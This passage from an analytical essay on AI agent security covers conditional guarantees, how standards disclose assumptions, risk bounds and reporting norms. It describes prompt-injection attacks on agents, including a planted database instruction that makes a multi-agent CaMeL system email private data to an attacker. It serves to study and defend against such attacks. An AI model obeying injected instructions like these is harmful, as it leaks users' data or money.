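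The check itself also needs care, because finding one way to satisfy the formula does not show that every outcome is safe. Suppose the rules limit payments to $5,000 and the agent proposes to pay €4,800. If the formula leaves the exchange rate open, the solver can choose a rate of 1.0 and allow the payment. At a real rate of 1.1, the payment comes to $5,280 and breaks the limit. A stricter monitor would ask whether any outcome could break the rules,

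$$s \wedge [\![j]\!] \wedge \neg\Phi,$$

and run the action only if the solver found none. The two checks agree when the formula fixes every value that matters. Wu and colleagues' code does turn the values in each action into constants, so the prototype may meet this condition, but the theorem does not state it separately.

Even a perfect translation would describe only the action, not what the user wanted, so the monitor would block a payment to the attacker only if a rule forbade it. Wu and colleagues call translating natural language into formal meaning an open problem.

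They also state that their experiments illustrate the mechanism and do not measure security statistically. They tested a small number of scenarios that they designed themselves, in which no attack succeeded and the monitor blocked no legitimate transfers. The abstract describes the foundation as conditional, but many people will see only the title, which doesn't mention this.

### AI makes proofs cheaper, but not specifications

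Machine-checked proofs used to take too much work for most software. Verifying seL4, a small operating system kernel, took about 20 person-years. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, expected AI to change this, because a proof checker rejects invalid proofs, so it doesn't matter if a language model often writes nonsense. Off-the-shelf models around that time wrote verified code for 27% of tasks in Lean and 82% in Dafny, according to figures quoted in *Can we secure AI with formal methods*.

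*LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (Anthropic, October 2026) reports that Anthropic's model Claude wrote machine-checkable proofs of security properties for 123 open-source software libraries, in a project with the company Theorem. Claude first had to fix bugs in some of the libraries. The claims have clear limits. For example, the proof for a RISC-V chip library shows that single-threaded test programs built from the library cannot crash with a memory error on any input up to a set size. It doesn't cover larger inputs, programs with several threads, or whether a program gives the right answer.

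De Millo and colleagues worried that nobody would study proofs about programs. That objection is weaker now that proofs are easier to produce and a checker can confirm each step without a human reader. But the check doesn't establish whether the theorem covers what its users need, or whether the model matches the system. If an AI writes both the proof and the specification, people may never have to consider either question. An AI under pressure to finish a proof might even weaken the statement until it is easy to prove, so somebody should compare the final statement with the original request.

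People can test a specification without reading the proof. Fonseca and colleagues suggest breaking the program on purpose and checking whether it still passes verification. For the payee list, a tester could change the monitor so that it sends every approved payment twice. The proof that no money goes to an unapproved account would still succeed, because that property doesn't limit how many payments the monitor makes. If the user also wants to prevent duplicate payments, someone has to add that requirement to the specification before asking an AI for another proof.

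## How does systems security disclose its assumptions?

Deployers need to know the conditions of a security claim before they can check them. Internet standards, product certificates, verified kernels and commercial operating systems all come with documents meant to state these conditions. Some of these disclosure practices are decades old, so there is evidence about how well they work.

### Internet standards name the attacks they leave out

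The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) publishes standards for how computers communicate, in documents called RFCs. Every RFC must have a "Security Considerations" section, and *Guidelines for Writing RFC Text on Security Considerations* (RFC 3552; Rescorla and Korver, 2003) explains what belongs in it.

Authors must say which attacks are out of scope and why, and which in-scope attacks the protocol does and doesn't stop. They must consider at least eavesdropping, man-in-the-middle attacks, and messages that are replayed, inserted, deleted or altered. They must also identify possible denial-of-service attacks and state what any login method assumes, and they should describe the risk that remains after protections are applied. In the sample text for the old Unix login, limits on password guessing help "only to the extent that attackers are impatient".

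Authors are not allowed to simply assume that a firewall keeps attackers out. Rescorla and Korver point out that people often move protocols from closed networks to the open Internet, that a network may have connections its owners don't know about, and that insiders are already behind the firewall. Anthropic's evaluators ran into unknown connections when their supposedly isolated tests turned out to have Internet access.

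One example in the guidelines is VRRP, a protocol that lets a second router take over when the main one fails. Its security section recommended a plain-text password where local machines were unlikely to interfere. Rescorla and Korver reprint the section as a good example, but their notes say they would have preferred a plain statement that the password helps only if no machine on the local network is hostile. They call this assumption unrealistic in many situations and "extremely brittle", because an attacker who takes over any one machine can reconfigure the routers.

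They then explain what this means for someone choosing a setting. Even with strong authentication, a hostile local machine can redirect traffic by other means, such as forging the messages that match network addresses to machines. Authentication also creates a new risk, because two routers with different passwords will reject each other's messages and both try to take charge. They conclude that authentication is a bad idea for this protocol unless somebody first removes the other threats. A network administrator can act on that conclusion more easily than on a bare list of assumptions.

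The guidelines have changed little since 2003. BCP 72, the IETF's current best practice on the subject, consists of the original document and a narrow 2023 addition about identifiers in protocol messages. Nir and Westerlund (2016) drafted a full replacement under the same title, but it expired the following year. In 2020, Arkko proposed changes because the threat model, which concentrates on communications, may no longer match reality. The model gives the attacker nearly complete control of the network but assumes that the computers at each end are uncompromised. It fits agents badly because the forged invoice can arrive over a secure connection and do its damage when the agent reads it.

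### Certificates list what the customer must provide

The Common Criteria is an international standard for evaluating the security of products. A vendor submits a document called a security target, which describes the product, the threats it should resist and the assumptions about its surroundings. An independent laboratory then checks the product against the document. The vendor can also claim that the product meets a protection profile, a reusable set of requirements for one type of product, such as operating systems. The result includes an evaluation assurance level from 1 to 7, which measures how thoroughly the laboratory checked the requirements, not how demanding they were.

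The assumptions can only be about the product's surroundings, so a vendor can't assume that the product itself works. The security target must also state each assumption as an objective for the environment, which is in effect a task for whoever runs the product.

The US National Security Agency's *Controlled Access Protection Profile* (1999) is an example of disclosed assumptions in operating system security. It succeeded a class of requirements in the Orange Book. The sec-certs database of security certificates lists the labels of the profile's seven assumptions in its entry *Controlled Access Protection Profile, Version 1.d*.

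| Label | What it assumes |
|---|---|
| A.LOCATE | The computer is in a place that outsiders cannot enter |
| A.PROTECT | Nobody physically tampers with the parts that enforce security |
| A.MANAGE | Competent people manage the system |
| A.NO_EVIL_ADM | Administrators are neither careless nor hostile, and follow the instructions |
| A.COOP | Authorised users cooperate, in a benign environment |
| A.PEER | Every connected system has the same management and the same security rules |
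| A.CONNECT | Connections to devices such as printers stay inside the controlled site |

The short labels let the rest of the document refer to each assumption, and a customer can go through the list one line at a time. An agent that reads suppliers' emails would not meet A.PEER, because the suppliers run their own systems.

### seL4 admits that one assumption is false

The seL4 project's website lists the assumptions behind the proofs of its verified kernel. The proofs assume that the hardware works as specified and has not been tampered with. They also assume that the small amount of hand-written assembly code is correct, that the kernel manages the processor's caches properly, and that the start-up code puts the kernel into the right initial state.

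Another assumption concerns direct memory access, which lets a device such as a network card write to memory without going through the processor. A faulty or malicious device could overwrite the kernel, so the proofs assume that no such device is present or that it behaves correctly. A developer building on seL4 therefore knows to leave such devices out, verify or trust their drivers, or add hardware that restricts which memory the devices can reach.

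The list also shows which assumptions each proof needs. The proof that the kernel keeps secrets also assumes that the hardware model includes every channel through which information could leak. The developers state that this assumption is false, because the model leaves out timing. The proof therefore covers only the channels in the model, and a deployer worried about timing attacks needs another defence. Someone who only needs the kernel to work correctly can ignore this assumption.

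### Microsoft says which bugs it promises to fix

Microsoft's Security Servicing Criteria for Windows tell security researchers which flaws will get a security update. Microsoft intends to release a fix if the flaw defeats the purpose of a security boundary or security feature and is severe enough. Otherwise, it may fix the flaw in a later version but doesn't promise to.

A security boundary separates code and data that have different levels of trust. For example, there is a boundary between one user's files and another's, and between a virtual machine and its host. Microsoft doesn't consider the separation between an administrator and the Windows kernel a security boundary, because it counts administrators as part of the trusted computing base. So a company that gives an agent administrator rights can't rely on Windows to keep the agent out of the kernel.

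Microsoft also lists defence-in-depth features, which make attacks harder but have known limits. Bypassing one of these is not enough by itself for Microsoft to issue a fix. The same distinction would be useful for agents. A vendor could treat the payee list as a boundary and the model's training against injection as defence in depth, so customers would know which failure the vendor considers a bug.

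### The Windows 2000 certificate

In October 2002, Microsoft announced that Windows 2000 had received a Common Criteria certificate at level 4. The laboratory had evaluated it against the NSA's profile, with some additions. Shapiro's *Understanding the Windows EAL4 Evaluation* quotes the profile, which applies to "an assumed non-hostile and well-managed user community" that needs protection from accidental or casual attempts to break in. The profile explicitly excludes determined attacks by hostile and well-funded attackers.

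Shapiro, an operating-systems researcher at Johns Hopkins University, told customers that this meant they should not connect the computer to the Internet, use email, or install software from a developer they didn't completely trust. He added that the level meant nothing without the profile, since a program that reliably paints the screen red could get level 4 and still be useless to someone who needs a black screen.

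He was harsher about the evaluation than he should have been. He wrote that level 4 does not require anyone to examine the software, but the standard required evaluators to look at part of the source code and run their own tests. He was also developing a rival operating system, which he expected to reach level 7. But he acknowledged that the profile was the most complete one for operating systems at the time and that commercial Unix systems were no better. Readers can check his main point, which is about the profile, just by reading the passage he quotes.

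Microsoft's *Overview* of the certification names the profile and lists many certified functions, including encrypted files and virtual private networks, but never mentions the assumption that users are not hostile. According to Microsoft, the certificate covered "the broadest set of real world scenarios", and certification in general gives more assurance that a product is secure. Microsoft did warn that certified products can still have vulnerabilities, but that is true of all software, and customers couldn't learn from the warning that this evaluation assumed no determined attackers.

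Another passage in the profile describes an environment with a "moderate" level of risk. In a mailing-list post, *Windows 2000 declared secure*, Shapiro (2002) called that word very unfortunate. He blamed a kind of grade inflation, saying the people behind the Common Criteria worried that users would think real assurance was impossibly difficult.

Some readers understood the certificate's limits. Redmond Channel Partner's *Windows and Common Criteria* (2003), a trade press article, explains that the certificate made Windows 2000 "securable", not secure. *On Shapiro's Understanding the Windows EAL4 Evaluation* (2004), a blog post replying to Shapiro, complains that people often overstate what a certificate and its level show about security. Yet the title of a Microsoft employee's post about later versions, *Windows Server 2003 and XP SP2 have achieved Common Criteria EAL4*, goes on to call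 the result "a measure of how secure" they are, though the text adds that configuration and maintenance matter just as much. TaoSecurity's *Thoughts on Recent Microsoft Common Criteria News* (2005) quotes the profile's condition that the entire network be under one management, which people probably don't expect when they hear that a product is secure.

In August 2003, the Blaster worm spread across the Internet through a flaw in Windows 2000 and Windows XP. The conditions of Windows 2000's security certification excluded attacks from strangers' computers, so Blaster did not contradict it. But the certification offered little reassurance to customers who had bought Windows 2000 to use on the Internet. Similarly, the makers of secure processors published that their security guarantees excluded physical attacks, but many blockchain networks overlooked this exclusion.

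In both cases the vendor or the profile's authors had disclosed the condition, but a short label reached far more people than the document did. Shapiro suggested writing the result as "CAPP/EAL4", with the profile's initials before the level. A buyer would then at least know that there was another document to look up, even though the label wouldn't explain the condition.

### What a mandatory section achieves

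In *Thou Shalt Discuss Security*, Whitaker, Prasad and colleagues (2019) analysed 8,437 RFCs published over 49 years to study whether the IETF's rules changed what authors wrote. The IETF first required a security section in 1993, with one sentence of instructions, and issued the detailed guidelines ten years later.

| | Before the 1993 rule | Between the rule and the guidelines | After the 2003 guidelines |
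|---|---|---|---|
| RFCs with a security section | 27% | 94% | 99% |
| Average length of the section | 39 words | 170 words | 324 words |
| Share of ten security topics covered | 0.9% | 6.8% | 13.0% |

Discussion of security outside the required section also grew. But the rule can't fully explain why RFCs included the section, because the share that had one rose from zero to over 90% in the year before the rule, perhaps because authors already agreed on it or knew it was coming. The sections' length and coverage rose only after the rule, but there was no comparison group, and Internet security became more important over the same period.

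The first security section in an RFC, from 1990, read, "Security issues are not discussed in this memo." Even after 2003, the average section touched on little more than one of the ten topics. The researchers' keyword search may have missed some discussions, though, and many RFCs don't need to discuss all ten.

A security section of normal length can be wrong. RFC 8342, which describes how to store the settings of network devices, has one of 115 words, close to the median. It states that the design has no security impact. Other researchers later found that the design allowed a denial-of-service attack, because it didn't specify who should delete expired rules. Telling writers to disclose their assumptions doesn't help with those they haven't noticed, as with the repeated key installation in Wi-Fi.

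McFadden and Mills (2020), in *Textual Analysis Methodology for Security Considerations Sections*, counted the words in Security Considerations sections published from 2003 to 2019 and found no significant change in wording after major security incidents. They also noticed that many sections refer to an earlier RFC, and they suspect that some of these references are lip service. Word counts are a crude measure, and the paper is an expired draft that mainly proposes a method for further research. It is unknown whether the sections made products safer, and Whitaker and colleagues doubt that anyone could measure this satisfactorily.

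Academic papers have no equivalent rule, and peer review has not made up for its absence. *Dos and Don'ts of Machine Learning in Computer Security* (Arp, Quiring and colleagues, 2020) checked 30 papers from the previous decade of leading security conferences for ten common mistakes and found at least three in every paper. More than half had an inappropriate threat model, at least in part, meaning that the researchers had not properly considered attacks on the learning system itself. A malware detector, for example, may look accurate until malware authors start changing their programs to fool it. The review covers only 30 papers, all of which use machine learning, so it does not measure how common such mistakes are in security research generally.

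A newer review with several of the same authors, *Chasing Shadows* (Evertz, Risse and colleagues, 2025), covers 72 papers on language models from leading security and software-engineering conferences in 2023 and 2024. Every paper had at least one of nine pitfalls, and the papers explicitly discussed only 15.7% of the pitfalls found in them. One of the nine is failing to identify the exact model used, which leaves readers unable to tell whether the result applies to the model they have.

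### Useful disclosure and boilerplate

The better documents do four things that the weaker ones neglect. They say who has to make a condition true, describe it precisely enough to check, explain what happens if it fails, and put it where people will read it along with the claim. For the invoice agent, the difference might look like this:

| | Boilerplate | Useful disclosure |
|---|---|---|
| Who is responsible | Administrators are trusted | The finance manager approves each change to the payee list |
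| What to check | The platform is secure | The agent's account cannot write to the payee list |
| What happens if it fails | Other attacks are out of scope | Anyone who can edit the list can add their own account and be paid |
| Where it appears | In an appendix | In the sentence that says no unapproved payment is possible |

A condition is easy to neglect when nobody is responsible for it, because the vendor expects the customer to handle it and the customer thinks the product does. The Common Criteria addresses this by turning assumptions into objectives for the environment. Microsoft's criteria instead specify which failures Microsoft will fix.

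Some conditions are hard to check even when they have an owner. A.COOP requires users to cooperate, but no test can establish that all of a company's employees will. A condition that software enforces is better. A November 2025 message on an IETF mailing list makes this point about SRv6, which lets a packet carry instructions for its own route. The writer argues that an organisation may have a policy about where it uses SRv6, but without an enforced boundary, outsiders can send in packets with any instructions they like. An administrator can test an enforced boundary by sending such a packet from outside.

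Stating what can happen if a condition fails helps a deployer decide which conditions deserve the most attention. The seL4 list includes this information for direct memory access, where a failure can destroy the kernel and with it every guarantee. By contrast, leaving timing outside the model affects only secrecy.

The Windows 2000 disclosure failed because the announcement gave only the level and left out the condition, which the profile stated clearly in the body of the document. A paper can fail in the same way if it states its condition in a limitations section at the end but reports an attack success rate of zero in the abstract without the condition. Xu and colleagues avoided this by putting PPMF's conditions in the abstract.

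The argument for these features is based on a few cases. Researchers could easily test it by giving deployers different versions of the same disclosure and asking them whether their system meets the conditions.

### What carries over to agents

The structure of these documents would also work well for papers on agent security. Researchers can list the attacks they exclude and explain why, as is required in an RFC, and give each assumption a short label, as in a protection profile. If they prove several properties, they can list the assumptions for each one separately, as the seL4 developers do.

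A lasting certificate for a fixed product suits AI agents much less well. The Common Criteria evaluation covered Windows 2000 with Service Pack 3 and one extra patch. According to Microsoft, operating systems submitted in 1999, when the Common Criteria became a standard, only got their results about three years later. On that schedule, an agent's certificate would describe a model that its provider had already replaced. The model, or a tool that runs on someone else's server, may also change without any action by the deployer. RFCs have a related limitation, because their text never changes after publication and corrections go into a separate document.

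seL4 offers a partial solution. Its proofs apply to particular configurations of the kernel, and the developers can run the proof checker again whenever the code changes. The same would work for a small monitor or a formal policy, but not for the model.

Microsoft's criteria are better suited to changing software because they are a commitment about how the company will respond, which still applies when the code changes. But a promise to fix a flaw doesn't prevent attacks before the fix arrives, and in that time an agent can send a payment that nobody can reverse.

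Responsibility is also divided among more parties than it was for a certified operating system, which one vendor supplied and the customer's administrators ran. An agent may combine one company's model, a second company's host application, and tools from a dozen publishers, under a policy the deployer wrote and exceptions the user approved. Assigning a condition to "the administrator" therefore no longer makes it clear enough who must keep that condition true.

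Because an agent's parts change separately, its disclosure should also list the changes that could break each condition. For the payee list, replacing the model breaks none of the four conditions. A new tool could break the first if it can send money without going through the monitor. An update to the monitor could break the second, and importing a new supplier list could break the third. Giving a colleague, or the agent itself, permission to edit the list would break the fourth. A deployer who adds a tool then knows which condition to check and doesn't have to evaluate the whole agent again.

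## How can a deployer turn a conditional result into an estimate of risk?

A conditional guarantee gives the probability of a violation when every assumption holds. To estimate the overall risk, a deployer also needs to know how likely the assumptions are to fail.

### Adding up the ways to fail

Let $V$ be the event that the invoice agent makes at least one unapproved payment in the coming year. Let $A$ be the event that all the assumptions $A_1, \dots, A_n$ hold throughout the year, and $\neg A$ the event that at least one fails. Then

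$$P(V) = P(V \cap A) + P(V \cap \neg A)$$

The first term equals $P(V \mid A)\,P(A)$, which is at most $P(V \mid A)$. The second is at most $P(\neg A)$, and the chance that at least one assumption fails is at most the sum of their separate chances. So

$$P(V) \le P(V \mid A) + \sum_{i=1}^{n} P(\neg A_i)$$

The bound holds even if the failures aren't independent. If one update breaks two assumptions, the sum includes the probability of that update twice, which makes the bound looser but still valid.

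Here is the bound for the payee list, with invented probabilities. The last row covers conditions nobody wrote down, like the one missing from the Wi-Fi proof.

| Condition | How it might fail | Chance of failure in a year (invented) |
|---|---|---|
| $A_1$: every transfer passes the monitor | A new tool can send money itself | 2% |
| $A_2$: the monitor allows only listed accounts | The code has a bug | 0.5% |
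| $A_3$: the list starts with approved accounts only | Someone mistypes an account number | 3% |
| $A_4$: only the user can add accounts | A colleague has permission to edit the list | 5% |
| No condition is missing | The proof overlooks part of the system | 2% |

The proof shows that $P(V \mid A)$ is zero, so the bound is $0 + 12.5\%$. The entire 12.5% comes from the chance that the assumptions fail, so a better proof of the same theorem would not lower it.

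Relying on a measured result instead of a proof adds a little more risk. If none of 3,000 independent test attacks succeeded, the upper bound on the success rate is about 0.1% per attack. With ten forged invoices a year, that adds about 1 percentage point, for a total of 13.5%. This calculation uses the confidence bound as a cautious guess, though it is not really a probability. Testing ten times as many attacks, again with no successes, would lower the total to 12.6%. Removing the colleague's editing rights instead would lower it to 8.5%, if that removed the whole 5%.

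The bound also assumes the worst about each failure. A sensitivity test can replace that with a measurement, because it estimates how often a violation follows when a particular assumption fails:

$$P(V) \le P(V \mid A) + \sum_{i=1}^{n} P(\neg A_i)\,P(V \mid \neg A_i)$$

In the tests of PPMF, no attack succeeded because source labels were missing, so that failure adds nothing to the risk estimate. Attacks almost always succeeded when a confirmation was forged, so the estimate includes nearly the full probability of a forged confirmation.

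Long lists of assumptions soon make the bound useless. The theorem in *CONTINUITY* has nine conditions, including the two cryptographic ones. To keep the bound below 10%, their average failure rate would have to be no more than about 1%.

### Numbers for accidents, worst cases for attackers

A deployer could estimate some of the probabilities in the table from records. For example, a company that has entered 2,000 account numbers can count how many were wrong. But no such record exists for a failure that an attacker causes, or looks for and exploits.

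Past experience can also mislead. When researchers published KRACK and the low-cost attacks on secure processors, the risk rose sharply for every user at once, even though the devices had not changed. Ten years without an incident at a hundred companies would therefore have been poor evidence about the eleventh year.

Estimates are even less reliable if a language model is part of the trusted computing base, because the model's failure rate depends partly on what the attacker writes. Christodorescu and colleagues compare relying on a model in this way to building memory protection on a processor feature that works only some of the time. They have in mind the no-execute bit, which stops a computer from running data as code. Defences can rely on that bit because it works every time.

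For failures of this kind, a list of worst-case outcomes is more useful than a probability. The deployer assumes that the condition has failed and works out what the attacker could then do. Suppose the colleague with editing rights adds their own account to the payee list. If the agent pays at most $5,000 at a time, once a week, and someone checks the accounts every four weeks, the colleague can take about $20,000 before anyone notices. The deployer can decide whether that loss is acceptable, or lower the payment limit, without guessing how honest the colleague is.

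Rough probabilities still help a deployer decide which condition to fix first. But if a single failure would ruin the company, a low estimate that nobody can check is not a good reason to accept the risk.

### Combining defences

One component's guarantee can supply another's assumption. Suppose the operating system guarantees that only the finance manager can edit the payee list, provided that it enforces file permissions ($B_1$) and nobody else has the manager's password ($B_2$). If the manager is the user who approves accounts, that gives $A_4$:

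$$(B_1 \wedge B_2 \Rightarrow A_4) \;\text{ and }\; (A_1 \wedge A_2 \wedge A_3 \wedge A_4 \Rightarrow P) \quad\text{give}\quad A_1 \wedge A_2 \wedge A_3 \wedge B_1 \wedge B_2 \Rightarrow P$$

The deployer now has five conditions instead of four. This is still an improvement if the chance that either $B_1$ or $B_2$ fails is lower than the chance that $A_4$ would have failed. The guarantee also has to match the assumption exactly. For example, remote attestation shows which monitor code is running, but it does not establish $A_2$, which requires that code to be correct.

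If a deployer adds a second defence, an attack has to get past both. Multiplying their miss rates gives the share of attacks that succeed only if the two defences fail independently. Suppose a gate reads the confirmation log before each payment, and a separate program later compares payments with the same log and can reverse them. A forged confirmation gets past both. If each defence misses 1% of attacks, and forged entries cause half of each one's misses, both fail in at least 0.5% of attacks. That is at least 50 times the 0.01% that multiplying the rates would give.

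Anthropic makes a claim of this kind in its *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1. A system card is a report on a model's abilities and safety that its developer publishes at release. Some of Anthropic's products scan incoming data for injected instructions and use a classifier to block dangerous tool calls. Anthropic says an attack would have to defeat both "independently". The layers act at different points, but that doesn't make their failures statistically independent. An injection that looks like an ordinary part of the user's task might get past both. Multiplying their miss rates would be justified only if someone had measured how often the attacks that beat one layer also beat the other.

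### Secure agents that pass on an attack

Combining secure agents can also break an assumption that held for each one alone. CaMeL assumes that its planning model receives a trustworthy request. In many systems now, a central agent, the orchestrator, delegates work to specialised agents. Each specialised agent treats the orchestrator's message as its user's request, even though that message can contain text from a web page or database.

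Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built a system from three CaMeL agents running on GPT-5.2. They asked the orchestrator to send Julie a Slack message summarizing all job applicants. One agent fetched the records from a database, where the researchers had planted an instruction to email the data to an outside address. Neither this agent's plan nor the orchestrator's changed, because their planning models never received the records. But the orchestrator put the summary into its message to the agent that sends notifications. That agent's planning model treated the planted instruction as part of its user's request and added a step that emailed the data to the attacker.

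Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They ran CaMeL without policy checks, so the experiment tested only whether attackers could change the plan. Checks based on trust labels would probably not have helped, because data loses its label when it becomes part of a request.

They also prove that the weakness is general. The theorem covers any tree of two or more agents that includes a tool returning untrusted data, provided the agents are flexible enough to use the result of one call in the next. In any such tree, some request will make an agent read the untrusted result and pass it to another agent as an instruction, so untrusted data helps determine the plan. The theorem does not show that every request is dangerous.

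The repair, multi-CaMeL, gives messages between agents two parts. For the invoice agent, the difference would look like this:

```
# CaMeL agents, each protected separately
payments_agent(f"Pay this invoice: {invoice_text}")

# multi-CaMeL
payments_agent("Pay the invoice using the values provided.",
    variables={"account": account, "amount": amount})
```

The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. The receiving agent's planning model receives only the instruction, while the values are passed separately and keep their labels. Each parent therefore ensures that the assumption behind its child's guarantee holds. The forged account number would still reach the bank tool, so the deployer would also need a policy that checks recipients.

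The researchers tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, with 949 attack cases for each of five models. On average, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with separately protected agents, and never with multi-CaMeL. The 0.2% was about nine attacks, all cases of boundary laundering.

That low rate shouldn't reassure a deployer much, because the benchmark's attacks were not designed to cross between agents and none succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without a defence. An attacker who knew how the orchestrator wrote its messages could target that step. In another test, separately protected agents stopped an attack that depended on taking over the database agent, but with only five trials, the upper bound on the attack's success rate is 45%.

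On a second benchmark, of industrial maintenance tasks, protecting the agents separately reduced the share of tasks completed by 21.6 percentage points on average, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, the corresponding losses were 13.4 and 0.85 points. The guarantee covers only agents arranged in a tree. The code also inherits the flaw that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's tracking of data, so an instruction that depends on untrusted data could still get past its checks.

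### What system cards report

System cards are where many deployers will look for a measured rate, and the rates depend heavily on how the developer ran the test. These are results for three Anthropic models:

| Model and task | Attempts | Safeguards against injection | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6, coding | 200 | Off | 0% |
| Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 1 | Off | 17.8% |
| Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 200 | Off | 78.6% |
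| Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 200 | On | 57.1% |
| Opus 4.8, browser | 1 | Off | 31.5% |
| Opus 4.8, browser | 1 | On | 0.5% |
| Fable 5.1, mixed tasks | 1 | Off | 0.1% |
| Fable 5.1, mixed tasks | 15 | Off | 1.0% |

The Opus 4.8 figures come from VentureBeat's *Anthropic’s browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged*, and the Opus 4.6 figures come from another VentureBeat article. Someone could truthfully report either a 0% or a 78.6% attack success rate for Opus 4.6.

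The Fable 5.1 results, from September 2026, come from a benchmark run by the security company Gray Swan. It contains 1,804 attacks that people wrote in public contests and that worked on several models. Anthropic left out models that the contestants had targeted, because attacks tailored to a model make it look worse than the others. So the 1.0% success rate applies to an attacker who has 15 tries and uses attacks that worked on other models, not to one who adapts to Fable 5.1. Most successes were in tasks with a graphical interface, where the rate after 15 tries was 4.1%.

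Some of these Fable 5.1 results include answers from the older Opus 4.8, which took over when classifiers for cybersecurity and biology blocked a request. This happened in 23% of runs overall and in about half of the coding runs. Anthropic's products use the same fallback, and it made no clear difference to the attack success rate.

OpenAI's April 2026 card for GPT-5.5 covered less. According to VentureBeat, its only section on prompt injection described tests of known attacks on connectors, which link the model to outside services. The section reported a robustness score, where higher is better, so readers have to convert it before comparing it with an attack success rate.

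Anthropic's card reports that attacks on Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash succeeded 9.2% of the time after 15 attempts, the lowest rate for any model not made by Anthropic. But Gray Swan apparently tested other developers' models through their public services, which may or may not include extra safeguards, so this is not a comparison of the models alone. A deployer choosing between vendors would need each one's results for the same tasks, number of attempts, safeguards and type of attacker.

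The cards also go out of date quickly. Anthropic has already replaced Fable 5.1 with Fable 5.2. The contents list in Mowshowitz's *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (2026) shows that the new card again has a section on prompt injection.

### How one zero lost its conditions

In July 2026, Anthropic released Opus 5 with a system card that reported no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios. The headline of The Decoder's article, *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, limits the claim to browsers but credits the model. The article explains that the system card's result applies only with Auto Mode, the setting that adds Anthropic's two layers of protection. Without them, attacks succeeded 3.7% of the time against Opus 5 and 0.93% of the time against the less capable Sonnet 5. The article doesn't say how many attempts the attacker had in each scenario or whether the attacks were adaptive.

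Boris Cherny of Anthropic also promoted the result. Willison (2026) quotes him calling Opus 5 "very hard to prompt inject successfully", with no rate, task or setting, but links to the relevant section of the card. ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card* quotes more of the same post, in which Cherny says the success rate drops to "~0" when the model is combined with the scan and Auto Mode in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. The shorter quotation omits these safeguards, and neither quotation mentions the 129 browser scenarios.

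For a company that connects Opus 5 to its own software without Auto Mode, 3.7% is the more relevant figure for browser tasks. Even with Auto Mode, zero successes in 129 scenarios is compatible with a true success rate of up to 2.3%.

The Decoder's article also reports that 2.0% of attacks on Opus 5 succeeded after 15 attempts on Gray Swan's benchmark. Weeks later, in September, Anthropic reported 4.8% for the same model, after adding nine scenarios and 670 attacks.

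### A procedure for reading a result

Suppose a company wants to use the zero result for Opus 5 to judge its invoice agent, which reads email and runs on the company's own software.

1. Find the property. Here it is that no injected instruction succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. That is a measured rate, and it doesn't cover other mistakes, such as paying an invoice twice.
2. List the assumptions, including any that the summary omits. They are the model, the browser tasks, Auto Mode, the number of attempts and the type of attacker. The threat model and the description of the experiment are the best places to look.
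3. Match each assumption to the deployment. The company uses Opus 5, so the model matches. But its agent reads email, it has no Auto Mode, and an attacker can send as many emails as they like.
4. Treat any unmatched assumption as untested. In the bound, that means setting its chance of failure to 1, so the zero no longer limits the company's risk at all. The company can change the deployment until the assumption holds, test its own agent, or rely on a defence whose conditions it does meet, such as the payee list.

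## What should a paper on agent security report?

A company that wants to apply a published result of zero successful attacks to its own agent often has to gather the assumptions behind it from the threat model, the limitations section and several appendices. Authors could gather them far more easily, because they know what they assumed. The eight norms below are proposals for how to report them. Most have a precedent in an earlier paper or standard.

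1. Put the conditions in the same sentence as the headline number, in the abstract too.
2. Give a table of assumptions: who makes each one true, how the authors checked it, whether the defence fails open or closed without it, and the measured effect of breaking it.
3. Separate what the authors proved, measured and assumed.
4. Report results in the oracle condition next to results from the deployed system.
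5. State what the attacker knows, how many attempts they get and what they can spend.
6. Name what the result excludes, with an example of a harm that it does not cover.
7. Give counts, confidence intervals and benign success.
8. Give exact versions, and say which changes void the result.

PPMF, by Xu and colleagues, is a useful paper to try them on because it already reports much of this information, though some appears only in the appendices.

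### Three ways to report one zero

A paper should state a number and its conditions in the same sentence, so that anyone who copies the whole sentence passes on both. Many people see only a paper's abstract or a single sentence copied from it, which is how people came to repeat the zero for Opus 5 without its conditions.

An abstract could report PPMF's main result in any of these ways:

| Version | Wording |
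|---|---|
| Shortened | PPMF reduces the attack success rate to 0%. |
| Published, partly paraphrased | If the platform's source, confirmation and risk labels are intact, "no evaluated unauthorized high-risk action passes the PPMF gate", while confirmed actions and low-risk uses of memory still work. |
| Improved | With correct source, confirmation and risk labels, which we supplied ourselves, PPMF blocked all 629 unauthorised high-risk actions taken from recorded AgentDojo runs (95% upper bound on attack success: 0.5%) and allowed all 97 confirmed ones. When we forged 10% of the confirmations, 8.8% of attacks succeeded. PPMF does not help if an attacker tricks the user into confirming a harmful action. |

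The shortened version is accurate for every test with correct labels, but most readers would take it as a claim about PPMF in general. The published version includes the condition, and the word "evaluated" limits the claim to the actions in the tests. It omits how many actions there were, who supplied the labels and what happens when the labels are wrong. The improved version adds these facts and one exclusion in about 35 more words.

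Authors also have to choose which number to put in the abstract. For PPMF, the 629 recorded attacks are a more honest choice than the 1,824 malicious web pages in its largest test. The larger number would look more impressive, but the gate treats all those pages identically.

### A completed table of assumptions

The second norm combines several older practices. The seL4 developers list the assumptions each proof needs, and the Common Criteria assigns someone responsibility for each assumption. The table's last column comes from sensitivity tests like those on PPMF. The table for PPMF would look like the one below, where "Inferred" marks entries that follow from the gate's rule but that Xu and colleagues did not test.

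| Assumption | Who makes it true | How the authors checked it | If it fails | Measured effect of breaking it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Source labels are correct | The platform, which records the channel each memory came through | Supplied the labels, then removed or changed some | Missing: closed. Too trusting: open, if the false label gives the action enough trust | 10% missing: no attacks succeed, 88.7% of legitimate actions work. 10% marked as user history: no change |
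| Confirmations are genuine | The platform, which logs the user's response | Supplied the labels, then removed or forged some | Missing: closed. Forged: open | 20% missing: no attacks succeed, 78.4% of legitimate actions work. 10% forged: 8.8% of attacks succeed |
| Risk labels are correct | Tool developers, and whoever reviews the policy | Fixed the labels before testing, then lowered some | Missing: closed. Too low: open | 10% lowered to read-only: 11.2% of attacks succeed |
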